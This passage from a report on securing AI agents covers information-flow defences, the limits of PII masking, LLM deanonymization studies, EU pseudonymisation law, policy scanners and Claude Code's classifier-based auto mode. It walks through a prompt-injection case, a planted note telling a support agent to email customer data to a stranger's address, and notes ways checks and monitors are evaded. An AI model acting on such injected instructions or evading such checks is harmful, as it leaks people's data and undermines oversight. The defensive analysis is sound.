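| FIDES with policies | 59.0% | 41.0% | 52.5% | 47.6% |

FIDES completed an average of 50% of tasks across the four environments, against 42% for an ordinary agent under the same kind of policies. It did worse on travel because GPT-4o often mishandled the variables. With o1, a stronger reasoning model, FIDES completed 68% of travel tasks. Newer models would presumably use the variables better still, but they would not help with tasks that the policies block by design. In banking, for example, many tasks ask the agent to read a file and follow its instructions, but the agent can no longer make a payment once it has read the file.

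The perfect security result also depends on the labels. Costa and colleagues marked a field as untrusted if any attack in AgentDojo used it, but an operator doesn't have a list of the fields attackers will use. If the shop labelled the notes on customer records as trusted because its own staff usually write them, the stranger's instruction would go straight into the model's context.

*Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (2026) applied the FIDES policies to AgentDojo's own GPT-4o agent, which completed 33.2% of tasks. The agent completed 62.5% under the paper's own policy, which is based on where data came from, and 83.7% with only AgentDojo's built-in defence. The test apparently didn't use FIDES's variables. If so, the agent that completed 33.2% was more like the ordinary agent in the second row of the table than like FIDES itself.

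Neither system hides everything an observer could infer from the agent's behaviour. Tallam and Miller give the example of a program that reads a secret number and fetches a web page that many times. No call contains the number, but the website's owner can learn it by counting the visits. FIDES likewise controls where values go, but not what someone can infer from the sequence of calls.

### Adoption and the cost of rules

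Few people use these designs so far. The security company Sophos reports in a 2026 SC Media article that no mainstream agent harness, including Claude Code, Cursor, GitHub Copilot's agent and Gemini CLI, has adopted CaMeL or the Dual LLM pattern. Sophos sells security products and recommends other measures in the article, but its claim would be easy to refute if wrong. Microsoft has published a tutorial with code for FIDES.

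One obstacle is writing the rules and keeping them up to date. The shop has three tools, but a large company may have hundreds, and Tallam and Miller expect policies at that scale to become inconsistent and full of duplicates. Willison, who has worked in application security for two decades, says he still struggles with Amazon's cloud access rules, and he doubts that ordinary users should have to think about such policies at all. Asking users to decide doubtful cases leads to fatigue, and they start approving everything.

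Tallam and Miller propose asking the user for approval less often. Reading public or internal data would need only a basic check of its source. Changing the user's own files would need a quick confirmation if the change used untrusted data. Sending an email or making a payment would need the full check and stronger approval. They did not test how this would change CaMeL's results. They also estimate that a second model adds more than ten seconds when it reads ten emails, although that figure is based on the speed of GPT-4.

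A harder case is when untrusted text legitimately chooses the recipient, as it sometimes does. Keller might write in her ticket that she is travelling and give her husband's address for the confirmation. The shop's rule would block the email because his address is not in the `email` field of her record. CaMeL and FIDES would also block it under a policy that requires a trusted recipient. The software treats both her request and the stranger's note as untrusted text that contains an address. *The LLMbda Calculus* finds that four independently built systems fail on the same few AgentDojo cases, including the payment that a document describes, and treats this as a general limit of information-flow defences.

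A person can often tell the two requests apart, so the shop could send such calls to an employee for approval, along with the ticket or note that prompted them. The employee needs to see the real address because they can't tell from `[EMAIL_2]` who would receive the email.

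## What a text with placeholders still reveals

PII tokenization hides single values, and the model still reads everything around them. Suppose Maria Keller's ticket had included a little more about her, and the harness had replaced her name and numbers without a miss:

> This is `[NAME_1]`, `[EMAIL_1]`, `[PHONE_1]`. The kettle arrived with a cracked lid on the Tuesday after the fire at our school. I'm the head teacher at Ashcombe primary, so I only opened the box today.

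Anyone who looks up the school's website will find her name. Masking "Ashcombe" as well would help less than it seems to, because the text would still mention the fire and the ticket would still be dated, and a local newspaper probably reported the fire and quoted the head teacher.

### Quasi-identifiers

A quasi-identifier is a detail that many people share but that can identify one of them when combined with other details. Keller's job, her town and the date of the fire are quasi-identifiers. *RAT-Bench* (Krčo, Yao and colleagues, 2026) cites the best-known example, Latanya Sweeney's 2000 finding that ZIP code, gender and date of birth together single out about 87% of Americans.

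A rough count shows why three such ordinary facts are enough. Suppose a ZIP code has 8,000 residents, half of them women, with birth dates spread evenly over 80 years, or 29,200 days.

| Known about the person | People who fit |
|---|---|
| Lives in the United States | about 340 million |
| Lives in this ZIP code | 8,000 |
| Is a woman | 4,000 |
| Was born on this date | herself and, on average, 0.14 others |

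The chance that none of the other 3,999 women shares her birth date is (1 − 1/29,200)³⁹⁹⁹, or about 87%. The exact match with Sweeney's figure is partly luck, since real ZIP codes vary in population and real ages are not evenly spread.

Multiplying these shares assumes that the details are independent, and often they aren't. Krčo and colleagues point out that a 30-year-old female chief executive is easier to identify than a 50-year-old male one. Rare values also leave fewer candidates than common ones, so living in Rhode Island reveals more than living in California. Recall weights all values equally, so a detector that masks a person's gender and state but misses her date of birth scores two out of three despite leaving the most revealing value. Beskorovainyi's leak rates have a similar limit because they cover only literal values left in the text. Details also add up across tickets if the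 same placeholder links them.

### What language models can infer

Finding a person from such details used to take a skilled investigator. *Beyond Memorization* (Staab, Vero and colleagues, 2023) was the first study to measure how well language models do one part of this work, guessing personal attributes. In one example, a commuter complains about waiting for a "hook turn", and GPT-4 infers that he lives in Melbourne, where drivers use this manoeuvre.

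"Beyond Memorization" tested GPT-4 on 520 Reddit profiles labelled by hand for eight attributes, including location, age and income. GPT-4's first guess was right for 85.5% of the labels. After a commercial Microsoft tool removed every location, date, age, organisation and person it could detect, GPT-4's accuracy on location fell from about 86% to about 55%. Removal worked best where the writer had stated the attribute outright. In those cases, accuracy across the tested attributes fell from 85.0% to 43.9%. On the attributes people had found hardest to infer, it fell only from 69.2% to 61.5%, though there were few of these.

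Knowing someone's town and income is still some way from knowing who she is. Krčo and colleagues measured the remaining step by drawing 100 profiles from US census data and having a model write a medical conversation, a chatbot exchange or a meeting transcript around each. Every text conveyed five quasi-identifiers. The texts that stated details explicitly also contained one direct identifier, such as a phone number, while those that only implied them had none. After an anonymization tool had processed the text, GPT-4.1 guessed the missing attributes. A person counted as re-identified if the model recovered a direct identifier, or if its correct guesses gave a better than one-in-five chance of picking the right person out of the US population. These are the shares re-identified:

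| Tool | Details stated plainly | Details in unusual form | Details only implied |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 100% | 98% | 32% |
| Microsoft Azure | 22% | 33% | 21% |
| Presidio | 41% | 77% | 30% |
| GPT-4.1, told to remove PII | 26% | 58% | 19% |
| Llama 3.1 8B, same instructions | 37% | 72% | 21% |
| Average of all tools tested | 44% | 69% | 28% |

When details were stated plainly, the tools removed most of the direct identifiers, and the remaining risk came mainly from quasi-identifiers. The tools removed almost none of the implied details, and Presidio reduced the risk from those by two percentage points. Azure's rates were low, but it often deleted text that wasn't sensitive.

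Krčo and colleagues included a profile only if its five quasi-identifiers already gave at least a 90% chance of a correct match, so these percentages are not estimates for ordinary text. The differences between tools and the rise in risk with the number of quasi-identifiers are more informative than the percentages themselves. Presidio's rate reached 60% with nine quasi-identifiers and no direct identifier in the text.

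*Large-scale online deanonymization with LLMs* (Lermen, Swanson and colleagues, 2026) tested whether models can name real people. The researchers took 338 users of the forum Hacker News who had linked to their LinkedIn profiles, and removed the links, names and handles. An agent with web search correctly identified 226 of them (67%) and named the wrong person in 25 cases, at a cost of $1 to $4 per attempt. In a larger test of matching users between the two sites, their method found 45.1% of the users, with 99% of its claimed matches correct. A method from before language models found 0.1% at the same precision. The researchers acknowledge that people who publish their own LinkedIn profile are probably easier to find than average. Their method found only 2.8% at that precision on a harder task, linking the same person's accounts across Reddit's film forums.

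*AgentDoxx* (Wen and Li, 2026) generated 822 interviews about work, each based on public facts about a real person who had once introduced themselves on Reddit. After direct identifiers were removed, models were asked to name the interviewee. The five best configurations named the right person in 47% to 48% of the interviews. Three open-weight models, which anyone can download and run, did so in 15% to 28% from training alone, without web search. The models' confidence was also a fairly good guide to accuracy. For the six strongest configurations with search, 89% to 97% of high-confidence names were correct.

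Everyone in that test had a public presence, and Wen and Li warn against applying their rates to the general population. A ticket about a kettle also contains much less information than an eight-question interview. Most of the shop's customers are probably hard to find from their tickets alone. Customers like Keller in the example, who mention a public role or an event that made the news, are exposed. The detector doesn't indicate which tickets contain such details.

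### Hiding more than literal values

Generalizing means replacing a detail with a vaguer one. "Head teacher at Ashcombe primary" could become "works at a school", and "the Tuesday after the fire" could become "in March". Whether the lost detail matters depends on the task. The job is irrelevant to a refund, but the month alone may not be enough to tell whether Keller is within a thirty-day limit.

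Wen and Li compared several ways of altering a text on 143 interviews that at least one model had previously solved. The last column averages twelve model configurations:

| Change to the interview | Characters changed | Interviewees identified |
|---|---|---|
| None | 0% | 75.1% |
| Presidio masks named entities | 0.42% | 62.0% |
| Presidio, then a paraphrase | 1.50% | 45.9% |
| A small trained model picks passages to redact | 2.64% | 35.1% |
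| Plausible false details replace true ones | 0.85% | 34.2% |

Masking named entities did little to prevent identification because the clues were in ordinary phrases, such as a role combined with a project and a time period. The best single model, Kimi K3, still identified 85.3% of the interviewees after masking. False details worked better on average, but several models treated the contradictions as transcription errors and still named the right person. False details would also be dangerous for an agent, which might refuse a refund because of an invented delivery date. Wen and Li counted changed characters but did not test how useful the altered interviews were.

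Instructing the models not to identify anyone lowered the average to 21.6%. In 37% of the cases where a model then withheld the name, it had already found the name in its search. Someone who wants to identify a customer would also leave that instruction out.

In a more thorough method, one model guesses attributes from the text and another rewrites the passages that revealed them, over several rounds. When Krčo and colleagues gave this method the exact list of attributes to protect, it cut re-identification to 2% for plainly stated details and 18% for implied ones. When they gave it Presidio's general list instead, the rates were 56% and 26%. An operator therefore has to know in advance which kinds of detail will identify people. GPT-4.1, which is an outside model, did both the guessing and the rewriting in this test.

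Sending fewer fields is simpler. For a refund, the model needs the order, the price, the delivery date and the nature of the damage, so the harness can drop the customer's birth date and purchase history from the record without any detection. For the free text of the ticket, a local model could fill in a short form:

```json
{
  "order": "48213",
  "problem": "arrived damaged",
  "wants": "refund"
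}
```

The form has no field for the school, the fire or the job, so those details never leave the shop. Anything else without a field is also left out, such as a request to send the confirmation before Friday. SEAL, the local rewriting system in Elmahallawy and colleagues' comparison, lost most of the text in the same way. A form suits routine requests, and the shop can send unusual ones to an employee.

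### Differentially private inference

Differential privacy is a mathematical limit on how much an output can depend on one part of the input. Take two documents *D* and *D′* that differ only in that part, and a randomized procedure *M*. For every set *S* of possible outputs, the procedure must satisfy

Pr[*M*(*D*) ∈ *S*] ≤ *e*<sup>ε</sup> · Pr[*M*(*D′*) ∈ *S*] + δ

A smaller ε means that an observer learns less about the protected part, and δ is a small allowance for failure. Thareja, Nakov and colleagues (2025), in *DP-Fusion*, apply the idea to a model that paraphrases a document:

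1. A detector marks the personal values.
2. The model computes probabilities for the next token from the document without those values.
3. It computes them again from the document with the values of one type, such as names, put back.
4. Software mixes the two sets of probabilities, giving the fuller document as much weight as a fixed limit on the difference allows.
5. It draws the next token from the mixture, and the cycle repeats.

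Suppose the next word is a town. Given the redacted document, the model assigns each of five towns a 20% probability. Given the full document, it assigns the right town 96% and the others 1% each. The mixture gives the right town about 24% under the strictest limit that Thareja and colleagues tested, and about 33% under the loosest. An observer therefore learns little from the word that appears. But under the strictest limit, the paraphrase will contain a wrong town about three times in four, which is a serious problem for an agent that has to act on the text.

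Thareja and colleagues tested DP-Fusion on court judgments with hand-marked personal data. An attacker who knew the rest of the document had to pick the hidden values from five candidates, where random guessing succeeds 20% of the time. The attacker succeeded 63% of the time against a paraphrase of the original, 28% against a paraphrase of the redacted text and 26% to 29% against DP-Fusion. Text quality was also close to plain redaction's. A judge model preferred DP-Fusion's paraphrase to the redacted one in 45% of comparisons at the strictest setting and 56% at the loosest.

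The advantage over redaction is therefore mainly the formal guarantee, which is weak at these settings. Thareja and colleagues report values of ε between 16 and 66. Even the lowest value would permit very large differences in probability, since *e*<sup>16</sup> is almost nine million. The attack results are better evidence of privacy than the formal guarantee.

DP-Fusion needs an extra run of the model for each type of personal data at every token, although these runs can happen in parallel. Its guarantee covers only the marked values, so Keller's sentence about the school would be unprotected unless the detector marked it. Because the model that writes the paraphrase reads the original, the shop would have to run that model itself and send only the result to the provider.

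### The legal position in the EU

The General Data Protection Regulation (GDPR) covers any information about an identified or identifiable person. Article 4(5) defines pseudonymization as processing data so that nobody can attribute it to a specific person without additional information, which the organisation keeps separately and protects. A vault or an encryption key is such information, so PII tokenization with restoration is pseudonymization, and the GDPR still applies to the shop's tokenized tickets. Data is anonymous only if nobody can identify the person, directly or indirectly, by means reasonably likely to be used.

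Deleting Keller's row from the vault may not make her old tickets anonymous, because the school and the fire still point to her. Krčo and colleagues note that the UK data protection regulator's guidance on testing for anonymity now requires organisations to consider whether language models could re-identify people.

In January 2025, the European Data Protection Board (EDPB), which brings together the national regulators, published its *Guidelines 01/2025 on Pseudonymisation* for consultation. Under these guidelines, data remains personal if the organisation responsible for it "or someone else" can link it back to an individual, according to Society for Computers & Law's *EDPB adopts pseudonymisation guidelines and provides guidance on cooperation with competition authorities*. Pseudonymisation can still help an organisation meet its security duties and justify processing on the basis of its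 legitimate interests.

Later that year, in *Case C-413/23 P* (2025), known as *EDPS v SRB*, the Court of Justice of the European Union (CJEU) had to decide whether pseudonymized data is also personal data for a recipient without the key. The case concerned the Single Resolution Board, the EU agency for failing banks. According to datenschutz notizen's *Pseudonymised data not always personal according to the latest CJEU judgement*, the agency collected comments from a bank's shareholders and creditors and replaced their names with random codes that only it could link back to them. It then passed comments to a third party. The European Data Protection Supervisor (EDPS), which oversees EU institutions, found that the agency should have informed the people concerned.

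The court ruled on 4 September 2025. Jones Day's *CJEU Clarifies Scope of Personal Data in EDPS v SRB Decision* (2025) summarizes three holdings:

- A personal opinion necessarily relates to the person who expresses it.
- Pseudonymized data is not always personal data from the recipient's point of view.
- The duty to inform people applies when an organisation collects their data.

The case arose under the regulation for EU institutions, but Baker Botts' *CJEU Clarifies Requirements and Definition of Pseudonymisation* explains that the GDPR has the same definitions, so the ruling matters for private companies too.

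Even after the ruling, the tickets are personal data in the shop's hands because it holds the vault, and it has to tell customers at the outset who will receive their data. A model provider has a weak argument that it cannot identify anyone from `[NAME_1]` if the ticket also mentions a school fire, especially if the provider runs models that can search the web. Lewis Silkin's *Digital Rulebook* (2026) describes the EDPB's draft guidelines on anonymization and the EU governments' latest proposal as treating data as personal for an organisation and its processors, but not for an independent recipient with no realistic means of identification. A provider that handles tickets only on the shop's instructions is normally a processor, so under that approach the tickets would be personal data for the provider too.

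The European Commission has proposed writing the relative approach into the GDPR's definition of personal data. *Towards a Contextual Concept of Personal Data Under the GDPR* (National Law Review, 2026) reproduces the proposed wording, under which information would not be personal for an entity that cannot identify the person, even if a later recipient could. The EDPB and the EDPS objected in February 2026 that the proposal goes further than the court did. On 21 October 2026 the Council, which represents the member states' governments, agreed to keep the existing definition and add a separate Article 25a on pseudonymized data, Lewis Silkin reports.

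That is only a negotiating position. The Brussels Times reports in *New EU data rules promise simpler compliance but raise privacy concerns* that talks will begin once the European Parliament has agreed its own position. Members of Parliament have tabled more than 1,000 amendments. Barczentewicz, in *Brussels Tries to Fix the GDPR Without Making It Worse*, expects negotiations to last into 2027. Until they end, the existing definitions apply as the CJEU has interpreted them.

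## Checking tool calls against fixed rules

PII tokenization does not prevent a second refund for order 48213, but a scanner can. The simplest scanner is ordinary code that checks each proposed call against rules written in advance.

### From interception to verdict

Yuan, Su and Zhao (2026), in *AEGIS*, describe an open-source scanner of this kind, which they released in March. Aegis patches the software libraries that agents use to call models, so developers don't have to change the agent's own code. Each tool call goes through six steps:

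1. **Intercept.** The patched library finds a tool call in the model's response, sends it to a separate server and pauses the agent.
2. **Extract.** The server collects every string in the arguments, including those inside nested lists and records, down to 32 levels. It stops at 10,000 strings so that an attacker cannot overload it, and it treats any call it couldn't read completely as suspicious.
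3. **Match patterns.** It compares the strings with 22 patterns for known dangers, such as database commands hidden in input, chained shell commands, paths to password files, phrases typical of prompt injection, and personal data. These matches count for more than the tool's name, so a harmless name doesn't hide a dangerous argument.
4. **Apply the policy.** Each policy is a JSON Schema, a standard description of the arguments a call may have. A schema can require `amount` to be a number no greater than 100, and can reject any argument it doesn't list.
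5. **Return a verdict.** Aegis blocks calls that violate a policy, allows those of low or medium risk, and holds the rest for a person. The agent waits up to five minutes for the decision.
6. **Record.** Aegis signs each record and includes a hash of the previous one, so anyone who later alters a record breaks the chain.

Aegis blocked all 48 attacks in a test by its developers. The developers took the attacks from published techniques and also wrote the patterns, so the result is little evidence of how well Aegis blocks attacks they didn't anticipate. Only two of the 48 attacks tried to send data out, which is what the stranger wants the shop's agent to do.

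Aegis flagged six of 500 harmless calls, a false-positive rate of 1.2%. At that rate, an agent that made fifty calls would have about a 45% chance of at least one false alarm, assuming the calls were independent. All six flagged calls were legitimate database queries that used OR in a condition, as some attacks do, so an agent that writes many such queries would get false alarms more often than the average suggests. The support agent writes none. Aegis added a median delay of 8.3 milliseconds, while a model typically takes at least a second to respond.

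### Three rules for the support agent

General patterns cannot tell the scanner how much a kettle cost. The shop has to add its own rules, which it could write in Cedar, an open-source policy language from Amazon Web Services (AWS):

```cedar
// 1. Refunds: up to 100 euros, within what is left of the price
permit (principal, action == Action::"refund.issue", resource)
when {
  context.amount_cents > 0 &&
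  context.amount_cents <= 10000 &&
  context.amount_cents <= context.order_unrefunded_cents
};

// 2. Email: only to listed recipients
permit (principal, action == Action::"email.send", resource)
when { context.permitted_recipients.containsAll(context.recipients) };

// 3. Email: no personal data in the subject or body
forbid (principal, action == Action::"email.send", resource)
when { context.personal_data_in_text };
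```

According to AWS's *Understanding Cedar policies*, the engine denies a call if any `forbid` rule matches. Otherwise, it allows the call only if at least one `permit` rule matches, so the shop would also need a `permit` rule for `crm.lookup`.

Cedar evaluates only the facts it receives with the request, so the harness has to look up the order's price and earlier refunds in the shop's database and pass the difference as `order_unrefunded_cents`. It fills `permitted_recipients` with the address in the customer record's `email` field. For rule 3, it runs a PII detector over the text and ignores the recipient's own name. All this happens on the shop's servers, so the harness can check the call against the rules after restoration without sending the real address to another company.

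Here are three calls under these rules:

| Call | What the rules find | Verdict |
|---|---|---|
| Permitted: an email to maria.keller@example.com, "Dear Maria Keller, we have refunded EUR 62.50 for your kettle." | The recipient is on the list, and the text contains no personal data except her own name | Allow |
| Mistaken: another refund of 62.50 euros for order 48213, because the first confirmation got lost | The amount is under 100 euros, but nothing is left of the price | Block |
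| Injected: an email to claims@parcel-desk.example, "Customer: Maria Keller, maria.keller@example.com" | The recipient is not on the list, and the text contains an email address | Block |

A 100-euro limit alone would have allowed the second refund. Rule 2 would also block an email that told the stranger only that order 48213 was a kettle, while a rule for restoring placeholders would not block that email.

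Cedar can only allow or deny a call. If the shop wants an employee to decide on refunds above 100 euros, other software has to hold the call until the employee decides. *If Agents Were Angels, No Governance Would Be Necessary* (Millstone, Akidau and colleagues, 2026) describes such a system, built around Cedar at the data company Redpanda. The system keeps a copy of the held call where the agent cannot reach it, and denies the call if no decision arrives in time.

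Other policy languages differ mainly in what they can express. Open Policy Agent, an open-source engine, has its own rule language, Rego. *Deontic Policies for Runtime Governance of Agentic AI Systems* (2026) adds obligations, such as a duty to notify a manager after a large refund. The system appends the obligation as text to the tool's result, so, unlike a refusal, it depends on the model to carry it out.

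### Blocking known dangers or allowing listed actions

A scanner can block only the calls that match a list of dangers, as Aegis's patterns do, or allow only the calls that match a list of permitted actions, as Cedar does.

A list of dangerous patterns can miss an email to a stranger, because the call may contain no database command, shell command or suspicious file path. A pattern for email addresses would match the call, but it would also match every legitimate call to `email.send`, since each has an address in the `to` field. A list of permitted recipients blocks the email without anyone having to anticipate the attack.

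If a denylist omits a danger, an attack succeeds, perhaps without anyone noticing. Gaps in an allowlist are easier to find and usually less harmful, because the agent fails to do its work and someone complains.

In guidance covered by Help Net Security, Rittenhouse and Johnson describe refusing tool calls by default as the most critical architectural pattern for agent security. They argue that it keeps working even when the model misbehaves or someone has poisoned the prompt, and they name Cedar and Open Policy Agent as ways to implement it. AWS's *Four security principles for agentic AI systems* likewise prioritizes deterministic controls outside the agent, because a model cannot reliably enforce the limits in its instructions.

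Both arguments rest on three properties of rules. First, the same call with the same facts always gets the same verdict, so developers can test the rules in advance. AWS's sample code, for instance, checks that a refund of 750 is refused. Second, after an incident, an investigator can find the rule that allowed the call. Third, persuasive wording doesn't change the verdict. The stranger can write that his request is urgent and that the manager approved it, but rule 2 compares only addresses.

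AWS has a commercial interest in this advice because it sells a service built on Cedar. It also argues in *Agentic security* that static rules designed for human activity cannot keep up with agents. But that warning is about detecting unusual behaviour. An operator can refuse unlisted calls without knowing what behaviour is normal.

Refusal by default makes agents somewhat less useful. Millstone and colleagues tested their system with four models on simulated versions of Jira and ServiceNow, two business applications. They counted a failure when protected data reached the model or its answer, or when a forbidden change took effect. In their main comparison, the system reduced failures from 57.6% to 0.2% of trials. Safety aside, the agent fulfilled the request in 60.9% of trials, down from 79.1%. The share of trials that were both useful and safe rose by about 22 percentage points. The system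 also filters what tools return, so the rules on calls account for only part of these results.

### Permissions for a single task

A fixed list of allowed tool calls has to cover everything the agent might ever need to do. An office assistant that sometimes pays invoices needs permission to pay, and an attacker can exploit that permission while the assistant is only summarizing emails. Several research systems therefore generate a narrower policy for each task.

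In Shi, He and colleagues' *Progent* (2025), a language model reads the user's request and writes rules that allow or forbid tools with particular arguments. Ordinary code enforces the rules and blocks any call that no rule allows. Suppose an employee asks an assistant to refund order 48213 and email the customer. The first rules could allow a lookup of that order, one refund tool and email to any address. After the lookup, the model proposes an update that limits the refund to 62.50 euros and the email to the customer's address.

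The update depends on text that an attacker may have written, so Progent compares the old policy *P* with the new one, *P′*. It applies the update automatically only if

*A*(*P′*) ⊆ *A*(*P*)

where *A* is the set of calls a policy allows. An SMT solver, a program that determines whether logical conditions can all hold at once, searches for a call that only the new policy would allow. If one exists, the update needs approval. This was the case for only 6% of updates in the tests.

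The check prevents an attacker from silently adding permissions, but it doesn't fix a policy that started out too broad. In the example, the first policy allowed email to any address. If the stranger's note misled the model into limiting email to his address instead of Keller's, the new policy would be narrower than the first, and Progent would apply it without asking.

Progent reduced the attack success rate on AgentDojo from 39.9% to 1.0% with GPT-4o as both the agent and the policy writer. On a second benchmark, ASB, the rate fell from 70.3% to 3.9%. The agents completed about as many tasks as without Progent. In these tests, every policy expansion was approved automatically to simulate a careless user. On AgentDojo, the first policy alone reduced the rate to 2.5%, so most of the protection came from rules written before the agent had read anything hostile. When a person reviewed every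 policy and expansion, no attack succeeded.

*Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) criticizes Progent because people make mistakes when they write policies by hand, and because hostile tool results may lead to an update that loosens the limits. The solver detects such updates, but someone still has to reject them.

ClawGuard (Zhao, Li and colleagues, 2026), released in April, asks the user to confirm the rules at the start. Before any tool runs, the model derives lists of permitted and forbidden commands, files and network addresses from the request. The user can edit these lists, but not a fixed set of baseline rules, such as a ban on reading stored credentials. ClawGuard then checks every command, file path and address in each call. It blocks the call if any of them is forbidden, and asks the user if any is on neither list.

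Zhao and colleagues tested this with five models on six attack benchmarks. Three of the benchmarks hide instructions in web pages or other content. The others use skills, which are files of instructions and scripts that extend an agent, or MCP tools. These are the average shares of attacks that failed:

| Benchmark | Where the attack hides | Without ClawGuard | With ClawGuard |
|---|---|---|---|
| SkillInject | Skill files | 56.7% | 86.7% |
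| MCPTox | MCP tools | 62.1% | 89.5% |
| MCPSecurityBench | MCP tools | 75.9% | 94.2% |

Without ClawGuard, the models already resisted at least 92.8% of the attacks in web pages and other content. Zhao and colleagues claim that ClawGuard raises this to 100%, but two of the fifteen results in their table are 99.1% and 99.8%.

ClawGuard reduced usefulness most on web tasks, which access many addresses that nobody listed in advance. Across web, operating-system and coding tasks, agents kept 87.4% of their original performance when every approval request was refused, and 95.1% when the user could approve up to three per task. Every request was also refused in the attack tests, so the security results apply to the setting with 87.4% performance. With approvals, security would depend on whether the user recognized a bad call.

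Neither system suits the shop's support agent as it stands, because both trust the person who gives the agent its task, and here that person is a customer. If a dishonest customer asked for a refund he wasn't entitled to, the model would derive rules that permit the refund, and he would confirm them. The shop has to write the support agent's rules itself, but it could use Progent or ClawGuard for assistants that take instructions only from employees.

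### Where rules fail

A tool call can be harmful even if every value in it is permitted. Suppose the stranger's note falsely claims that the kettle arrived broken. Rule 1 allows a refund of 62.50 euros for order 48213 because the amount is within the limit and the order has not been refunded before. Shi and colleagues exclude such attacks from Progent's scope, such as one that tricks an agent into choosing the attacker's product from several valid options. The SkillInject attacks that still succeeded against GPT-5.4 with ClawGuard in place mostly changed what the agent wrote. One skill told it to give environmentally friendly websites a high score without reviewing them, which required no suspicious tool call.

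General-purpose tools cause a different problem. A refund has a few arguments with clear meanings, but a shell tool's argument is a program. ClawGuard's baseline rules block a command that names the folder containing a user's private keys, but a program can assemble that name from pieces while it runs, so the name never appears in the call. ClawGuard looks for such disguises and asks the user when it finds one, but the same program can be written in endlessly many ways. The six false alarms in Aegis's test have the same cause, since a database query is also a small program. A shop can avoid much of this problem by giving its agent narrow tools such as `refund.issue` and no shell.

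Calls that are harmless individually can also be harmful together. An agent that refunded every order under 100 euros from the past month would break none of the shop's three rules. Aegis limits each agent to 100 calls a minute, which would still permit up to 10,000 euros in refunds every minute. The harness can keep a running total of the day's refunds and pass it to Cedar as another fact, but someone has to foresee the need for it.

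*Rethinking Access Control for AI Agents* (2026) distinguishes systems that check single calls, such as Progent, from those that also check the history of earlier calls. Tiffany, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *Sapien*, built one of the latter at Google. A model writes a policy from the user's request and the tools' documentation, before the agent reads any outside data. The policy describes whole sequences of calls. For the refund, it could look like this:

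```
crm_lookup@r
  . refund_issue(amount=PREDICATE(within_price))
  . email_send(to=PREDICATE(is_owner))
```

The dot means "then". `@r` saves the record so that the two predicates, both short Python functions, can compare later arguments with it. The agent can issue a refund only after the lookup, and only once, because the sequence contains one refund. A policy that only listed the three tools would let the agent call them in any order and refund any amount to anyone.

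Tiffany and colleagues assumed that an attacker had complete control of the agent, and counted the attacks that the policy made impossible. Sapien ruled out 93–95% of attacks on AgentDojo. On Toolathlon, which has longer tasks, it ruled out 62–85%, about twice as many as a list of permitted tools did. Agents completed nearly as many tasks with Sapien as without it. These figures are not comparable with Progent's attack success rates, which come from particular attacks on particular models. A real attack can fail because the model does not act on it, even if the policy would have allowed it.

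Hidden information can leak through permitted calls too. Millstone and colleagues found four answers that contained an exact protected value that had never entered the model's context. The agent had reconstructed it from other information. In another trial, the number of rows a filtered search returned was enough to reveal something about the hidden data.

Rules also need upkeep. If the mail server's developer adds a `bcc` field, the harness has to include it in `recipients`, or rule 2 won't cover it. A strict schema would reject calls that use the new field until someone updated the rules, which is safe but interrupts work. Even short rules can contain mistakes. An example in AWS's documentation is supposed to allow refunds of "$500 or less", but its condition is `amount < 500`, so it rejects a refund of exactly $500. AWS offers to translate plain-language requirements into Cedar for people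 to review, but a reviewer could easily overlook a difference like this one.

Some requirements cannot be written as rules of this kind. *Autoformalization of Agent Instructions into Policy-as-Code* (2026) translated a clinical agent's written policy, which had 56 points in eight sections, into Cedar. The translation left out every point that required interpreting the agent's text or making a vague judgement about content, and four sections produced no rules. The shop's condition that goods must have arrived damaged also requires judgement. Cedar can check a field called `damaged`, but someone or something has to read Keller's ticket and decide the field's value.

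## Checking tool calls with a second model

A language model can read Maria Keller's ticket and judge whether the kettle arrived damaged. An operator can therefore put a second model between the agent and its tools, give it the user's request and the proposed call, and have it decide whether the call should run. Coding agents need this most, because their main tool is a shell, where fixed rules are least reliable. Anthropic and OpenAI have built such reviewers into their coding agents, Claude Code and Codex, and both companies have published error rates.

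### Auto mode, step by step

Claude Code originally asked the user before it ran a command or changed a file. Users accepted 93% of these requests, and Anthropic observed that people who see many requests stop reading them closely. Users could avoid the requests by using a sandbox or by turning off all checks. A sandbox limits what a command can reach, but it needs configuring for each new capability. Auto mode has a model review the calls instead. Anthropic first offered it to Team customers as a research preview, according to its *Auto mode for Claude Code*. Anthropic's *Permission modes* now lists it as the default for interactive terminal sessions on every plan.

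A tool call goes through up to three tiers:

1. Calls to tools that cannot change anything, such as reading or searching files, run at once. So do calls that match a rule the user has written, for example one that allows a code formatter. Auto mode suspends any rule broad enough to permit arbitrary code, such as one that allows every Python command.
2. Edits to files inside the project folder also run without review, because the user can inspect and undo them through version control. *Shall We Approve?* (2026) describes the same exemption in a recent version, 2.1.288.
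3. Everything else goes to the classifier, a language model with instructions for judging calls. This includes shell commands, web requests, calls to external tools and edits outside the project folder.

According to Anthropic's configuration guide, rules that forbid a call or require the user's approval are applied before the classifier. A company can therefore keep fixed rules like the shop's and use the model only for calls those rules don't cover.

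The classifier works in two stages. In the first, the model reads a long prompt that ends with an instruction to err on the side of blocking, then outputs a single token, "yes" to block the call or "no" to allow it. After a "no", the call runs. After a "yes", the model gets the same prompt again, but with a final instruction to reason carefully before deciding. This second stage can release a flagged call, but it doesn't check calls that the first stage allowed. Because the two prompts differ only at the end, the system can reuse nearly all the processing from the first stage.

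Most of the prompt is a fixed template that instructs the model to judge what a call would do rather than how it is worded. So if the agent writes a script and then runs it, the model has to evaluate the script. The model must also treat anything the agent chose on its own as unauthorized until the user says otherwise. The operator can edit three parts of the prompt: the places the company trusts, the kinds of action to block and the exceptions. The default prompt has more than twenty block rules.

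An incident in Anthropic's log, in which an agent deleted remote branches, shows how these parts work together. The user had asked the agent to "clean up old branches" (lines of development in a code repository), and the agent issued a command to delete branches matching a pattern on the shared server. Auto mode should block this command because the deletion is irreversible and the user may have meant only the branches on his own machine.

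After a block, the session continues, and the agent receives the refusal as a tool result, with the reason and an instruction to look for a safer way instead of working around the block. After three blocks in a row, or twenty in one session, Claude Code stops and asks the user. If the agent is running unattended, the program ends. According to the current documentation, when Anthropic's server reviews the calls and returns no verdict on one, Claude Code refuses that call.

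The classifier reviews each delegated task before the main agent hands it to a sub-agent, while the user's request is still available for comparison. Inside the sub-agent, the task takes the place of the user's message, so a task the user never wanted would look fully authorized. The classifier also reviews the sub-agent's actions at the end, since something the sub-agent read may have misled it. If that review flags a problem, the main agent still gets the results, with a warning attached.

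### What the reviewer reads

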